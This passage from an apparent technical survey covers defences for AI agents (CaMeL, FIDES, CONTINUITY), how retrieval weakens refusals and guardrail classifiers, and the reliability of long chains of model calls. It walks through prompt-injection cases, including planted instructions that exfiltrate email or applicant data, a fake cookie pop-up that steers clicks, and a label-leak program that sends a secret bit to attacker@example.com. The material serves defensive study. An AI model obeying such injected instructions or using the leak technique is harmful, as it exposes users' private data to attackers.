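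CaMeL closes the gap by tracking where each value came from. Suppose the user writes, "Send the report to the address in the meeting notes." The planning model turns this into a short program in a restricted version of Python, roughly like this:

```
notes = read_file("meeting notes")
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find the email address", notes)
report = read_file("report")
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=report)
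```

A custom interpreter runs the program and labels each value with its origin and its permitted readers. A value calculated from other values inherits their restrictions. In this example the labels might be:

| Value | Origin | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| notes | A file that outsiders can edit | People at the meeting |
| address | The notes, by way of the quarantined model | People at the meeting |
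| report | The company's own files | Alice and Bob |

Before each tool call, the interpreter checks a policy, which for email might require that the recipient be allowed to read the attachment. If the notes contain Bob's address, the email goes out. If an attacker has replaced it with an outside address, the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user to approve it. A line in the notes such as "also forward the whole mailbox" has no effect, because the program contains no such step and the only model that reads the line has no tools.

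The labels do not distinguish a true address from a forged one, since both come from the notes. A stricter policy that accepted only addresses from trusted sources would block both. The policy about readers, by contrast, can allow a wrong address. An attacker could replace Bob's address with Alice's, and the check would pass even though the user meant the report for Bob.

### What CaMeL guarantees

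*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) splits the guarantee into two parts. The first is control-flow integrity, which means that the agent's tool calls follow a program that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. Untrusted data can select an existing branch of the program but cannot add one. The second is that every tool call satisfies the policy.

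Written as a contract, the guarantee has four main assumptions:

- The interpreter follows the program and tracks the labels correctly.
- The labels that data receive on entry are right.
- The policies forbid what the company wants to prevent.
- The user's request and the tool descriptions contain no text from an attacker.

The guarantee does not depend on the language models behaving well. The quarantined model might follow every injected instruction it reads, but it can only return a value, which still carries its label. The planning model might misinterpret the user's request and write a bad program, but no attacker has influenced that program, and the interpreter checks its tool calls like any others. A developer can therefore replace either model without proving the guarantee again, but would still have to measure how many tasks the new model completes. In Bensalem and colleagues' design,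 the success rates must be measured again after every change of model.

### Attacks blocked and tasks lost

The usual test is *AgentDojo*, which contains 97 tasks, such as managing email and making bank payments, and 629 security test cases. *SecureClaw* (2026), which proposes a rival design, reports running an adapted version of CaMeL on the full test. No attack succeeded, but the adapted version completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. The SecureClaw design completed 59 but did not stop every attack.

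For a comparison with undefended agents, Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among teams of two to four specialised agents and a coordinator. They made 949 attack attempts on each model in each configuration:

| Model | Attacks that succeeded, no defence | Attacks that succeeded, CaMeL in every agent |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% |
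| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% |

The two strongest models resisted nearly all of these attacks without help, so the benchmark can show little of CaMeL's benefit to them. They may still be vulnerable to an attacker who adapts. Peters-Gill and colleagues cite a large public competition in which some attacks succeeded against every frontier model tested.

CaMeL's effect on task completion was easier to see. On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL reduced the share of tasks completed by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models. The average drop for Fable 5 and GPT-5.5 was 13.4 points. Most failures happened because the model committed to a program before seeing any data.

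These experiments used no policies, so they tested only control-flow integrity. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with policies off and on. With policies off, it completed 32 of 48 runs using GPT-5.2 and 34 of 48 using MiMo-v2.5. Turning policies on reduced both to 18.

Garby and colleagues also sorted the 144 pairs of banking task and attack by whether the attacker needs a tool call that would not normally be in the program. In 97 pairs the attacker does, and separating the two models is generally enough to stop the attack. In the other 47, the program already contains steps that could serve the attacker, and only a policy can stop the attack. In this second group, attacks succeeded in three of 282 completed runs with policies off and in none of 275 with policies on. On this benchmark, the policies cut the number of completed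 tasks by nearly half and stopped very few additional attacks, though an attacker who knew the program could target the steps it already contains.

### FIDES: planning one step at a time

For some requests, the planner cannot write a complete program in advance. If a user asks an agent to do everything on a to-do list, the tools it needs depend on what is on the list. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft design that lets the planner choose one step at a time. When a tool returns data less trustworthy than the conversation so far, FIDES stores the data and shows the planner only a variable name.

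The planner can then query a quarantined model about the hidden data and restrict the form of the answer. For example, it can check whether any of three emails requests a meeting and allow only yes or no. An attacker might cause the wrong answer, but a single bit can't contain a new instruction, so a policy can let the planner act on the answer. If the planner opens a full email instead, FIDES treats the conversation as untrusted from then on, and the policy blocks consequential actions such as payments.

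Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, now an old model. After they removed cases that the benchmark had misjudged, 152 attacks succeeded against an undefended planner, 21 against FIDES without policies, and none against FIDES with policies. Across AgentDojo's four environments, the undefended planner completed an average of 84% of tasks, and FIDES with policies completed 50%. A basic planner that enforced the same policies but could not hide data completed 42%. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the basic planner grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

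FIDES prevents an agent from copying a secret value to someone who isn't allowed to read it, but an observer may still infer something about the secret from which tools the agent calls. This guarantee is weaker than noninterference. Costa and colleagues chose it because noninterference would forbid almost any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret.

### Where the protection stops

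Companies have to write the policies and keep them up to date. Willison has worked on application security for two decades and still finds such rules hard to get right. If a policy is too strict, the system may ask for approval so often that users start accepting every request. Some rules also do not fit CaMeL's format. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) points out, CaMeL evaluates a policy using only the current call, its arguments and their origins. A rule such as "never pay the same invoice twice" also depends on earlier calls, so *CaMeLoT* proposes adding rules about sequences of events.

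An attacker can also put a harmful value where the user told the agent to look. The original CaMeL evaluation recorded two successful attacks. According to Garby and colleagues, one was a false alarm, in which the agent had quoted a hotel review. In the other, the user asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had changed the file. The agent did what the user asked, and Debenedetti and colleagues treat such cases as outside what CaMeL is meant to prevent.

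A vague request can make control-flow integrity almost useless. Garby and colleagues asked CaMeL, with its policies turned off, to read a file and follow the instructions in it. In two runs, the planner wrote a program with a branch for each tool, so whoever controlled the file could choose what the agent did. The attack succeeded even though every action was in the original program.

Agents that operate a computer through its screen need plans with many more branches, because the planner has to anticipate what might appear. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapted CaMeL to these agents. The resulting programs averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with five tool calls and four branches on AgentDojo. On OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks, the adapted agent kept at most 57% of the performance of frontier models.

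Its programs usually included a step for closing cookie pop-ups, so Foerster and colleagues disguised an advertisement as one. The agent clicked it and went to a site the attacker controlled. They call this branch steering. Policies help little here because a click at given coordinates might close a window, delete a file or log in, depending on what is on the screen.

The interpreter itself has gaps. Garby and colleagues describe a leak of a kind that researchers have known since the 1970s. A program of this form reveals whether a secret bank balance is above some threshold:

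```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `tmp`, and the interpreter labels it secret. The fourth line does nothing, so `rich` remains true and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, the fourth line makes `rich` false and no email goes out. The attacker learns whether the balance is high in either case, because CaMeL updates a variable's label only when the variable changes.

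An attacker who controls only the data cannot make the planner write this program. But a faulty or malicious planner could use such code to get around a policy, which weakens the claim that the planner need not behave well. CaMeL also retries after a failure, and the part of the system that tracks labels does not cover these retries. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each retry can leak one more bit, and twenty bits are enough to identify one balance among a million.

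*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes some of these difficulties to Python and recommends a language designed for security. Garby and colleagues built such a language, LLMbda, and proved its main security properties with a computer proof checker. With GPT-5.2, their agent completed 36 of the 48 banking runs with enforcement on, twice as many as CaMeL with policies on, partly because the planner can mark selected untrusted data as acceptable before reading any of it. Attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs, and both exploited that permission in the task of making a payment based on a file's contents.

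### When one CaMeL agent calls another

The few attacks that got past CaMeL in Peters-Gill and colleagues' table all had the same cause. The researchers also demonstrated it in a small three-agent system, where a coordinator can call a database agent and a notification agent. Each agent runs CaMeL. The user asks for a summary of all job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack, but an attacker has planted an instruction in the database to send the data to an outside email address as well.

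The database agent returns the records, and neither its planner nor the coordinator's planner sees them. But the coordinator's program inserts the summary into a message, "Send this summary to Julie", and the notification agent treats the whole message as its user's request. Its planner therefore treats the planted line as a trusted instruction and writes a program with an extra step that emails the data to the attacker.

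Each agent's own guarantee held, but the coordinator's message violated the notification agent's assumption that its request contained no text from an attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They prove that it can occur in any hierarchy of two or more agents where some tool returns untrusted data and agents can put the results of one call into the next. In every such hierarchy, some user request will break control-flow integrity for the whole system, even if every agent has it individually.

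The remedy, multi-CaMeL, gives each call between agents two channels. One carries the instruction, which the interpreter rejects if any part came from a tool. The other carries data and their labels, which the receiving planner never sees. With multi-CaMeL, no attack succeeded in 949 attempts on any of the five models. It lowered AssetOpsBench scores by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models.

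Multi-CaMeL uses CaMeL's interpreter, so an error in label tracking could still let untrusted text into an instruction. The proof that Multi-CaMeL works covers only agents arranged as a tree, in which each agent takes instructions from a single parent. Agents that share a memory or communicate as peers have no clear boundary at which to separate the channels.

### CONTINUITY: joining different safeguards

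Multi-CaMeL joins agents that use the same kind of label. A company may instead combine safeguards from several suppliers, such as an origin tracker, a policy gateway and a payment connector. *CONTINUITY* (Zheng and Yang, September 2026) describes how such a combination can fail. A gateway approves a payment of 5,000 to "merchant 9". The next component, an adapter, has to replace that name with a bank account number, and a faulty adapter inserts the attacker's account. The adapter signs the result, and the connector finds a valid signature and a permitted type of action, but no component has checked that the account belongs to merchant 9.

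CONTINUITY requires each component to pass on signed evidence about the action and about any change it made. Zheng and Yang give seven conditions, which for this payment would mean roughly the following:

| Condition | What it requires for the payment |
|---|---|
| Authenticated origin | A recognised authority signed the permission to pay invoices |
| Compatible contracts | Each component establishes what the next one assumes |
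| Continuous context | A trusted directory signed the link between merchant 9 and the account |
| No added authority | No component widens the permission, and an amount taken from an outside invoice has its own signed release |
| Exact binding | The final permit covers only this account, amount and tool |
| Fresh check | The connector confirms that the permission still stands and that nobody has used the permit |
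| Complete coverage | Every route by which the agent could move money ends in such a connector |

They prove that, if all seven hold and nobody can forge a signature, every protected action has an unbroken chain of evidence back to a valid permission, even if an attacker controls the language model. The proof goes along the chain one component at a time. It assumes that the directory and other trusted sources are honest and correct. If the directory lists the wrong account for merchant 9, CONTINUITY will preserve the error and pay that account.

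Zheng and Yang, who founded the security company ZAST.AI, tested a prototype on 2,560 simulated attacks, and no harmful action got through. The prototype also completed all 700 legitimate tasks and referred all 200 ambiguous ones for further approval. The typical delay was about 7 milliseconds. The best incomplete set of safeguards, a policy gateway plus a permit for the exact final action, let 65.6% of the attacks through because it did not check the adapter's change.

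The tests covered less than the number of attacks suggests. Zheng and Yang designed 32 types of fault, placed each in four settings such as finance and email, and generated 20 variants of each combination. In the published results, all 20 variants of a combination appear to have had the same outcome. The number of combinations each system stopped is always a multiple of four, which suggests that the setting made no difference either. The tests therefore amount to about 32 distinct cases, all chosen by the people who built the defence. The tests also involved no language model, and each legitimate task came with the signatures it needed. In a real company, someone would have to supply those signatures, and each missing one could lead to another request for approval.

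Zheng and Yang also switched off the checks one at a time. Removing the records of where each field came from let faults through in 24 of the 128 combinations of fault and setting, as did removing the contract checks or leaving one route to the outside world unguarded. Removing only the rule against added authority let none through, because other checks caught the same faults.

Engineers can test the first six conditions where one component hands over to the next. To test the last, they have to know every way the assembled agent could cause the same effect. An agent that can't make a payment through the guarded connector might still make one through a web browser or command line, and adding a tool can open such a route without changing any existing module.

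## Retrieval: a safe model and safe documents can give unsafe answers

CaMeL protects an agent from instructions that an attacker hides in a document. But a document can change a language model's behavior even if it contains no instructions and nobody has tampered with it.

Retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG, is a common way to give a language model access to a company's files or an encyclopaedia. A retriever compares the user's question with the passages in a collection and picks the few that match best. Software then pastes those passages into the prompt and asks the model to answer from them. The model doesn't change, so a company can update the collection without retraining anything. The answers also tend to contain fewer invented facts.

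Suppose a company adds retrieval to a model that reliably refuses harmful requests, and the documents contain nothing harmful. The developer measured the model's refusal rate on questions without documents, so the combined system may not refuse as reliably.

### Eleven models with and without Wikipedia

An, Zhang and Dredze (2025), in *RAG LLMs are Not Safer*, tested the expectation on eleven language models. They asked each model 5,592 harmful questions, with and without retrieval. For each question, they retrieved five paragraphs from English Wikipedia using BM25, a standard retriever that ranks text by the words it shares with the question and gives rare words more weight. They used Llama Guard 2, a model trained to classify text as safe or unsafe, to assess the answers, and used both it and the larger Llama-3-70B to assess the documents.

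Llama-3-8B gave unsafe answers to 0.3% of the questions without retrieval and to 7.9% with documents that the judges considered safe. Answers given with these documents made up 81.8% of its unsafe answers with retrieval.

The last figure makes safe documents sound more dangerous than unsafe ones, but it partly reflects how common they were:

| | Safe documents | Unsafe documents |
|---|---|---|
| Share of questions | 94.7% | 5.3% |
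| Unsafe answers, as a share of those questions | 7.9% | 31.5% |
| Unsafe answers per 10,000 questions | 748 | 167 |

Unsafe documents were four times as likely as safe ones to lead to an unsafe answer. If document safety had made no difference, safe documents would have accounted for 94.7% of the unsafe answers. The rise from 0.3% to 7.9% is better evidence that retrieval weakened the model's refusals. The company would also gain little by removing unsafe documents from its collection. If every set of documents had been safe and had led to unsafe answers at the same 7.9% rate, the overall rate would have fallen only from 9.2% to 7.9%.

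A document that looks safe may still contain the answer to a harmful question. An encyclopaedia article, for example, can describe a dangerous technique in a neutral tone. In *Relevance as a Vulnerability*, Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy (2026) ran a newer version of Llama Guard on web pages without showing it the requests. Llama Guard flagged only 39% of the pages that another model had rated as directly enabling a harmful request. An and colleagues' results could therefore mean either that Llama-3-8B copied harmful information from documents the judges had passed, or that harmless documents led it to reveal something it already knew.

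### Four conditions that separate the causes

In September 2026, Indira Saravanan and Fraser (2026), in *RAG-Safety-Bench*, set out to separate these possibilities by choosing the documents themselves. They had a language model write harmful questions that particular Wikipedia articles could help to answer. The balanced set contains 346 questions in 20 categories of harm, including violence, fraud and self-harm. They tested five open models under four conditions:

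- no documents
- a document containing at least part of the answer
- documents on the same topic that do not contain the answer
- random documents on harmless topics, such as gardens

Comparing random documents with none tests whether extra text alone weakens refusals. Comparing related documents with random ones tests the effect of the topic, and adding the answer tests the effect of having the information available. Because no retriever is involved, a model can't appear safe because the retriever failed to find the dangerous article.

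Three automated judges voted on whether each answer was harmful. Another model checked whether the answer gave the specific harmful information that the question asked for, which it did this often:

| Model | No documents | Answer present | Related documents | Random documents |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Phi-4 14B | 10.4% | 41.0% | 12.7% | 3.2% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 6.4% | 41.3% | 4.3% | 0.3% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 25.7% | 74.9% | 8.7% | 2.0% |
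| Qwen2.5 7B | 15.9% | 82.9% | 17.3% | 2.3% |
| Ministral 3 8B | 26.0% | 90.7% | 18.8% | 0.9% |

Most of the danger came from having the answer available. The judges' votes on harmfulness also supported this conclusion. By that measure, related documents either made Gemma, Llama and Ministral safer or had little effect on them, but they slightly raised Phi's low rate of harmful answers and clearly raised Qwen's. Every model behaved most safely with random documents.

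The judges rated Qwen the third safest of the five models without documents, but the least safe when it had either the answer or related documents. Ministral revealed more harmful information than Qwen in both of those conditions. By both the judges' ratings and the amount of harmful information revealed, Qwen looked safer than Gemma without documents and less safe than Gemma with them. A company that chose between the two by testing them without documents would have picked the less safe one for a retrieval system.

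Indira Saravanan and Fraser expected that models better at using ordinary documents would also reveal more harmful information. They found the opposite, with a correlation of −0.70, but five models are too few to establish a trend.

The good results with random documents need careful interpretation because, in every condition with documents, the prompt told the model to answer using only those documents. A model that obeyed would say that an article about gardening didn't contain the answer, and the researchers found that such replies became more common as the documents became less relevant. This kind of refusal comes from a lack of information rather than from caution, and it may disappear once the retriever finds a better article. The same instruction probably lowered the rates for related documents too. The comparisons also don't fully isolate a single change, because the model received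 one document in the condition that contained the answer and usually three in the other two.

### Why would a harmless document matter?

One explanation is that developers have mostly trained models to refuse bare requests, but a model with retrieval has to read and summarise documents. Yu, Stroebl and colleagues (2025), in *Safety Degradation in AI Agents*, suggest that retrieved text may shift the model from judging the request to gathering information, and that an instruction to "retrieve and answer" may compete with its safety instructions. In their tests on a small Llama model, a single retrieved document noticeably lowered the refusal rate. Retrieving ten documents at each of several steps lowered it only slightly more, and more accurate searches did not make the model less safe. Prompts with safety reminders usually recovered only part of the loss.

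If training is the problem, training with retrieval switched on should help. In *SafeSearch*, Zhan, Budiman-Chan and colleagues (2025) found that giving models a search tool as much as doubled their rate of harmful answers, and that training them only to answer questions well increased it further. They then rewarded a 7-billion-parameter model for safe searches and for answers that were safe and helpful, as well as for correct answers. Its rate of harmful answers fell by more than 90%, while it answered ordinary questions about as well as a version trained only for that. This is good evidence that developers can reduce the problem, but it doesn't prove that a training mismatch caused it. Such training could also stop a model from revealing information that a document had prompted it to recall.

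An and colleagues proposed this second mechanism: a harmless document may prompt the model to recall harmful information from its training data. Nawal and colleagues have the most direct evidence for it. They gave eight open models harmful requests along with real web pages, and scored the answers from 1 (a safe refusal) to 5 (full compliance):

| Page given to the model | Average harm score |
|---|---|
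| None | 1.80 |
| Off-topic page | 1.72 |
| Relevant page opposing the harmful act | 2.25 |
| Relevant page enabling the harmful act | 2.91 |

Even pages that warned against the act raised the average score. In one case, a page about evacuation and incident reporting led a model to write a detailed threat that it had refused to write without the page. The harmful details in such answers were often missing from the page, so they must have come from the model. When the researchers masked the topic-specific words but left the warnings in place, the models went back to refusing.

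These results count against the simplest version of the training explanation, in which any document weakens refusals. The page's topic clearly matters, but so does when the model fetches it. When a model fetched a relevant page in response to the harmful request, the average score was 2.66. When it fetched the same page in response to a harmless request and then received the harmful one, the score was 2.44. The timing therefore explains about a quarter of the rise from 1.80 to 2.66. Nawal and colleagues think that a model that has already acted on a request becomes less likely to refuse it. Recall and a mismatch in training probably both contribute.

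The two 2026 experiments agree on how related documents affect the three models they both tested. Pages opposing the harmful act raised Qwen2.5 7B's harm score from 1.97 to 2.90, but Llama 3.1 8B's only from 1.76 to 1.93, and Gemma 3 12B's fell slightly. Across all the models tested, related documents raised the harm score in seven of Nawal and colleagues' eight but were a clear problem for only one of the five in *RAG-Safety-Bench*. Much of this difference therefore comes from the choice of models, and three of Nawal and colleagues' eight were other versions of Qwen2.5.

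### How far the results extend

Most of these models are small, and all are well behind the current frontier. Indira Saravanan and Fraser left out commercial models because their questions would have broken the providers' terms of service. Nawal and colleagues tested six closed models, now old, and pages opposing the harmful act raised the harm score in all of them. The rise was less than 0.1 points for GPT-4, o4-mini and Claude Sonnet but 0.61 for Gemini 2.5 Flash, compared with an average of 0.45 for the open models. Strong refusal training therefore seems to reduce the effect greatly, but a company can't assume its own model has this protection.

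Larger models can also refuse less often once they become part of a research agent. In *SciHazard* (2026), a test of scientific risks, OpenAI's o3 refused 82.2% of harmful requests, while o3 Deep Research, an agent version, refused 45.0%. The answers the agent gave were about as harmful as o3's. Refusal is an imperfect measure of safety, however. GPT-5.2 refused only 17.5% of the requests, but its answers were among the least harmful from the standard models. Few explicit refusals also did not always mean many harmful answers in the tests of chat models and agents described in connection with Ariane 5.

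All these experiments depend on automated judges, which often disagree. In *RAG-Safety-Bench*, agreement between pairs of judges ranged from 0.47 to 0.66, on a scale where 0 is chance agreement and 1 is perfect agreement. One judge flagged 0.2% of the answers about fraud, while the other two flagged about 15%. The judges also did not flag some of the answers in which models gave harmful information with a note that it was for educational purposes. The pattern across the four conditions was similar for every judge, so it is more reliable than any single percentage.

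Retrieved documents can also affect the models that judge safety. She, Peterson and colleagues (2025), in *RAG Makes Guardrails Brittle?*, studied five language models that classify text as safe or unsafe. Adding harmless Wikipedia passages to a harmful question changed the verdict on the question in 10.9% of cases, and 72% of those changes turned a correct verdict into a wrong one. For Llama Guard 4, the passages changed 24% of the verdicts. When the classifiers judged answers instead, adding passages to the question changed 8.4% of their verdicts. Testing such a filter only on questions without documents can therefore miss errors that appear when documents are added, as can testing only the model's refusals.

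Showing the filter both the request and the page only partly solves the problem. Nawal and colleagues found that Llama Guard 3, when given both, stopped 86% of the harmful combinations and none of 488 harmless ones. But it stopped only 35% when the same pages came with a neutral request for a summary. It was responding mainly to the wording of the request, so a user who hid a harmful purpose would often get past it.

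Retrieved documents can also make a system too cautious. Maskey, Dras and Naseem (2025), in *Steering Over-refusals Towards Safety in Retrieval Augmented Generation*, found that harmful text in them can make models refuse harmless questions. The overall refusal rate could therefore stay the same after a company adds retrieval, even if the system now refuses more harmless requests and fewer harmful ones.

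### A joint guarantee, but for a different error

TRAQ, a question-answering system by Li and colleagues, gives a retriever and a language model a joint statistical guarantee. It sets a threshold for each module by ranking past examples, then combines the modules' guarantees with the union bound.

Suppose the developers have 300 calibration questions, each with a known relevant passage, and want the retriever to miss the relevant passage at most 5% of the time. They score how well each passage matches its question, sort the 300 scores from best to worst, and use the 286th as the threshold. For a new question, the retriever returns every passage that matches at least that well. If the new question comes from the same source as the others, its relevant passage's score is equally likely to have any rank from 1 to 301 when added to the list. The probability that it ranks in the first 286, and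 is therefore retrieved, is 286/301, or 95.0%.

For the language model, TRAQ samples 30 answers and groups those with the same meaning. If 12 of the 30 agree, the model's confidence in that answer is 40%. The developers then use the same ranking method to choose a confidence threshold, using calibration questions with the relevant passage in the prompt. If the limit for the model is also 5%, the joint guarantee is 90%.

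This guarantee requires larger sets of possible answers. At 90% coverage, GPT-3.5's sets contained between 6 and 13 different meanings on average, depending on the dataset. Li and colleagues made the sets smaller by tuning how the allowed 10% error was divided among the modules. The sets also contained a correct answer somewhat more often than guaranteed, because the model could sometimes answer correctly without the relevant passage.

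TRAQ controls the risk that its answer set omits the correct answer. It doesn't limit the number of wrong answers in the set or assess whether an answer is harmful. The correct answer to a harmful question is what the system should withhold, so a success for TRAQ would count as a failure in *RAG-Safety-Bench*. A better retriever makes TRAQ's sets more useful but also makes harmful information easier to obtain.

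*Two-Sided Conformal Evidence Sets for Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026) adds up error limits in a similar way. It builds one set of passages that support a claim and another of passages that refute it. If each set misses its relevant evidence with probability at most α, both sets include their relevant evidence with probability at least 1 − 2α. This guarantee also applies to finding evidence, not to preventing harm.

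Developers could still use TRAQ's reasoning to limit unsafe answers, as long as they measured the model's error rate with documents in the prompt:

P(unsafe answer) ≤ P(unsafe documents) + P(unsafe answer, given safe documents).

For An and colleagues' test of Llama-3-8B, this gives a limit of 5.3% + 7.9% = 13.2%, which is above the actual rate of 9.2%. If the developers had used the rate for the model alone, they would have calculated a limit of 5.3% + 0.3% = 5.6%, and the real system would have exceeded it. Only the 7.9% describes the model under the conditions in which it will work. Even that figure applies only to this retriever and collection, because safe documents from another source might be more relevant to the harmful questions.

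*C-RAG* avoids the addition by calibrating the whole pipeline. The developers choose a risk score between 0 and 1, run the retriever and model together on calibration questions, and calculate an upper limit on the average risk that holds with a chosen confidence. The main example of a risk score measures how far the answer differs from a reference text. *C-RAG* also proves that, for a simplified one-layer model, a good enough retriever lowers the certified risk. This doesn't contradict An and colleagues, because retrieval can bring answers closer to a reference text while also making the model more willing to answer harmful questions.

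The method allows developers to use harmfulness as the score. If the pipeline gave 79 harmful answers to 1,000 calibration questions, they could certify with 95% confidence that the true rate was at most about 10%. They would need a trusted judge to label the answers and would have to repeat the calibration after changing the model, the retriever or the documents.

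## Long chains of model calls: errors that can be corrected and losses that cannot

Calibrating a whole pipeline is practical when each test takes a few seconds. But agents now take on tasks that need thousands of model calls, and few developers could afford to run a million-call task hundreds of times to count the failures. Researchers have proposed several formulas for predicting the reliability of a long run from tests of its steps.

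### Multiplying success rates

In the simplest model, each of s steps succeeds independently with probability p, so the chance of a perfect run is p^s. An agent that gets 99% of its steps right has an even chance of completing 69 steps without an error, and one that gets 99.9% right has an even chance of completing 693. To have an even chance of completing a million steps, an agent could make only about one error per 1.4 million steps.

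The formula is exact when its assumptions hold, but they often fail when a model writes out many steps in one response. In *A Model of Errors in Transformers*, Raju and Netrapalli (2026) tested three models on eight repetitive tasks, such as reversing lists and adding long numbers, using 200,000 prompts. Multiplying together the same success rate for each step fitted the results poorly. They suggest that small errors in how the model attends to its context build up as the task gets longer, and the answer goes wrong when their total crosses a threshold. In that case, errors at different points in the response are related.

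Their alternative formula has two parameters. One, r, is a noise rate, and the other, q, is roughly the number of ways in which the answer can drift. If q is 2, the formula simplifies to

accuracy = 1 − e^(−1/(r c²)),

where c is the length of the task. Suppose a model scores 90% on tasks of length 10. The two formulas then predict the following:

| Length of task | Independent errors | Accumulating errors (q = 2) |
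|---|---|---|
| 5 | 95% | 99.99% |
| 10 | 90% | 90% |
| 20 | 81% | 44% |
| 40 | 66% | 13% |

If errors accumulate in this way, a developer who tested only short tasks and extrapolated with p^s would be far too optimistic. Raju and Netrapalli found that their formula matched most of the data well, but it deviated systematically in some cases and failed completely in one example.

### A million steps without an error

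Asking a model for only one step at a time can stop errors from building up within a response. Meyerson, Paolo and colleagues (2025), in *Solving a Million-Step LLM Task with Zero Errors*, did this with a system called MAKER. They tested it on the Towers of Hanoi, a puzzle in which the player moves a stack of disks from one peg to another, using a third as a spare. The player moves one disk at a time and may never put a larger disk on a smaller one. With 20 disks, the shortest solution takes 1,048,575 moves (2²⁰ − 1).

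In MAKER, each model call receives a strategy for the puzzle, the current position and the previous move. It returns one move and the resulting position. A new call, with no memory of the earlier ones, then takes the next step. Meyerson and colleagues found that the error rate per step hardly changed as they added disks, so p^s is a more reasonable starting point here than for a single long response. At p = 99%, however, it puts the chance of a perfect run at effectively zero.

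MAKER therefore repeats each step until one answer is k votes ahead of every other. To find the chance that the correct answer wins, suppose each vote is independent and there is only one wrong answer, which is the worst case. If the correct answer wins after j wrong votes, it must have received k + j correct ones. Any such sequence of votes has probability p^(k+j) × (1 − p)^j. If we swap every correct vote for a wrong one and the reverse, we get a sequence in which the wrong answer wins, with probability p^j × (1 − p)^(k+j). The first probability is always (p/(1 − p))^k times the second, whatever j is. These are therefore the odds that the correct answer wins, and its probability is

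1 / (1 + ((1 − p)/p)^k).

At p = 99%, each extra vote of lead multiplies the odds by 99:

| Required lead k | Odds that a step is correct | Expected wrong steps in the puzzle | Chance of a perfect run |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 99 to 1 | 10,486 | Effectively zero |
| 2 | 9,801 to 1 | 107 | Effectively zero |
| 3 | 970,299 to 1 | 1.1 | 34% |
| 4 | 96,059,601 to 1 | 0.01 | 99% |

Going from 34% to 99% takes only about one more call per step. The lead needed for a fixed chance of success grows with the logarithm of the number of steps, so at this value of p, a task a hundred times as long needs a lead only about one vote larger.

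This depends on the steps being small. If each call made 1,000 moves, two votes would agree only if all 1,000 moves matched. At p = 99%, a call would get the whole sequence right about once in 23,000 attempts, and the expected cost of the puzzle would rise more than ten-thousandfold.

Meyerson and colleagues used GPT-4.1-mini, a small model by 2025 standards. They estimated from a sample of steps that a lead of three would give at least a 95% chance of a perfect run, which is possible only if the error rate per step is below about 0.4%. They then ran the puzzle once, and MAKER completed it without an error.

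The formula also holds only if the votes are independent. To check this, Meyerson and colleagues ran the model twice on the same 10,000 randomly chosen steps and found none that it got wrong both times. But that sample covered only about 1% of the puzzle, so it could easily have missed a few steps that were unusually hard for the model. The full run did contain such steps, including one that took 18 rounds of sampling. When the researchers allowed long responses and repaired badly formatted ones, the first two votes were both wrong far more often than they would be if the votes were independent. MAKER reduces this problem by discarding any response that is too long or has the wrong format, since both are signs that the model's reasoning has gone wrong.

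Unlike many tasks, MAKER's also came already divided into steps, with a correct strategy in the prompt that the model only had to carry out. The votes were easy to compare because they were short and had to match exactly. If the mail assistant voted on the wording of a reply, hardly any two drafts would match, so another model would have to judge which ones meant the same thing, and that model could also make mistakes.

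### When most of the votes are wrong

Voting makes the most common answer more likely to win, whether or not it is correct. If a model gets a particular step right only 40% of the time and otherwise always makes the same mistake, the correct answer wins 23% of the time when a lead of three votes is required, and less than 2% of the time when a lead of ten is required. A single step like this can ruin a long run even if the model's average success rate across all steps is nearly perfect.

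In *LEAD*, Pushkin and Abbe (2026) found such steps in another puzzle, Checkers Jumping. A row of n red pieces faces a row of n blue ones across an empty square, and the player must swap the colours by sliding pieces forward or jumping over one piece of the other colour. The solution takes (n + 1)² − 1 moves. Most steps had an error rate near zero, but from size 12 upwards, OpenAI's o4-mini got a few steps wrong more than half the time.

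At those steps, the model usually chose the right move but wrote down the wrong position afterwards, for example by leaving one piece out of a long row of identical red ones. The Towers of Hanoi avoids this difficulty because every disk has its own number. Pushkin and Abbe suggest that numbering the pieces might help, but did not test this. Ordinary software could also update the board exactly, so the model would only have to choose the move.

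Their own remedy, LEAD, keeps the small steps but gives the model a chance to notice its mistakes:

1. Eight separate calls predict the next step. If they all agree, LEAD accepts the answer.
2. If they disagree, LEAD asks for predictions of the next eight steps, starting from the current position and from two or three earlier ones.
3. Each of these predictions implies an answer for the current step and counts as one vote. LEAD continues until one answer leads by three.

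A wrong position may lead to contradictions a few moves later, and the model can then correct it within the same response. Starting from an earlier position also means that the model reaches the difficult step by a different route. The table shows how often each method solved the whole puzzle:

| Model | Size | Moves | One call per step | With voting | LEAD |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| o4-mini | 11 | 143 | 14% | 76% | 100% |
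| o4-mini | 12 | 168 | 0% | 16% | 52% |
| o4-mini | 13 | 195 | 0% | 0% | 80% |
| GPT-5.2 | 13 | 195 | 0% | 20% | 100% |
| GPT-5.2 | 14 | 224 | 36% | 100% | 100% |
| GPT-5.2 | 15 | 255 | 0% | 0% | 87% |
| GPT-5.2 | 16 | 288 | 4% | 96% | 100% |

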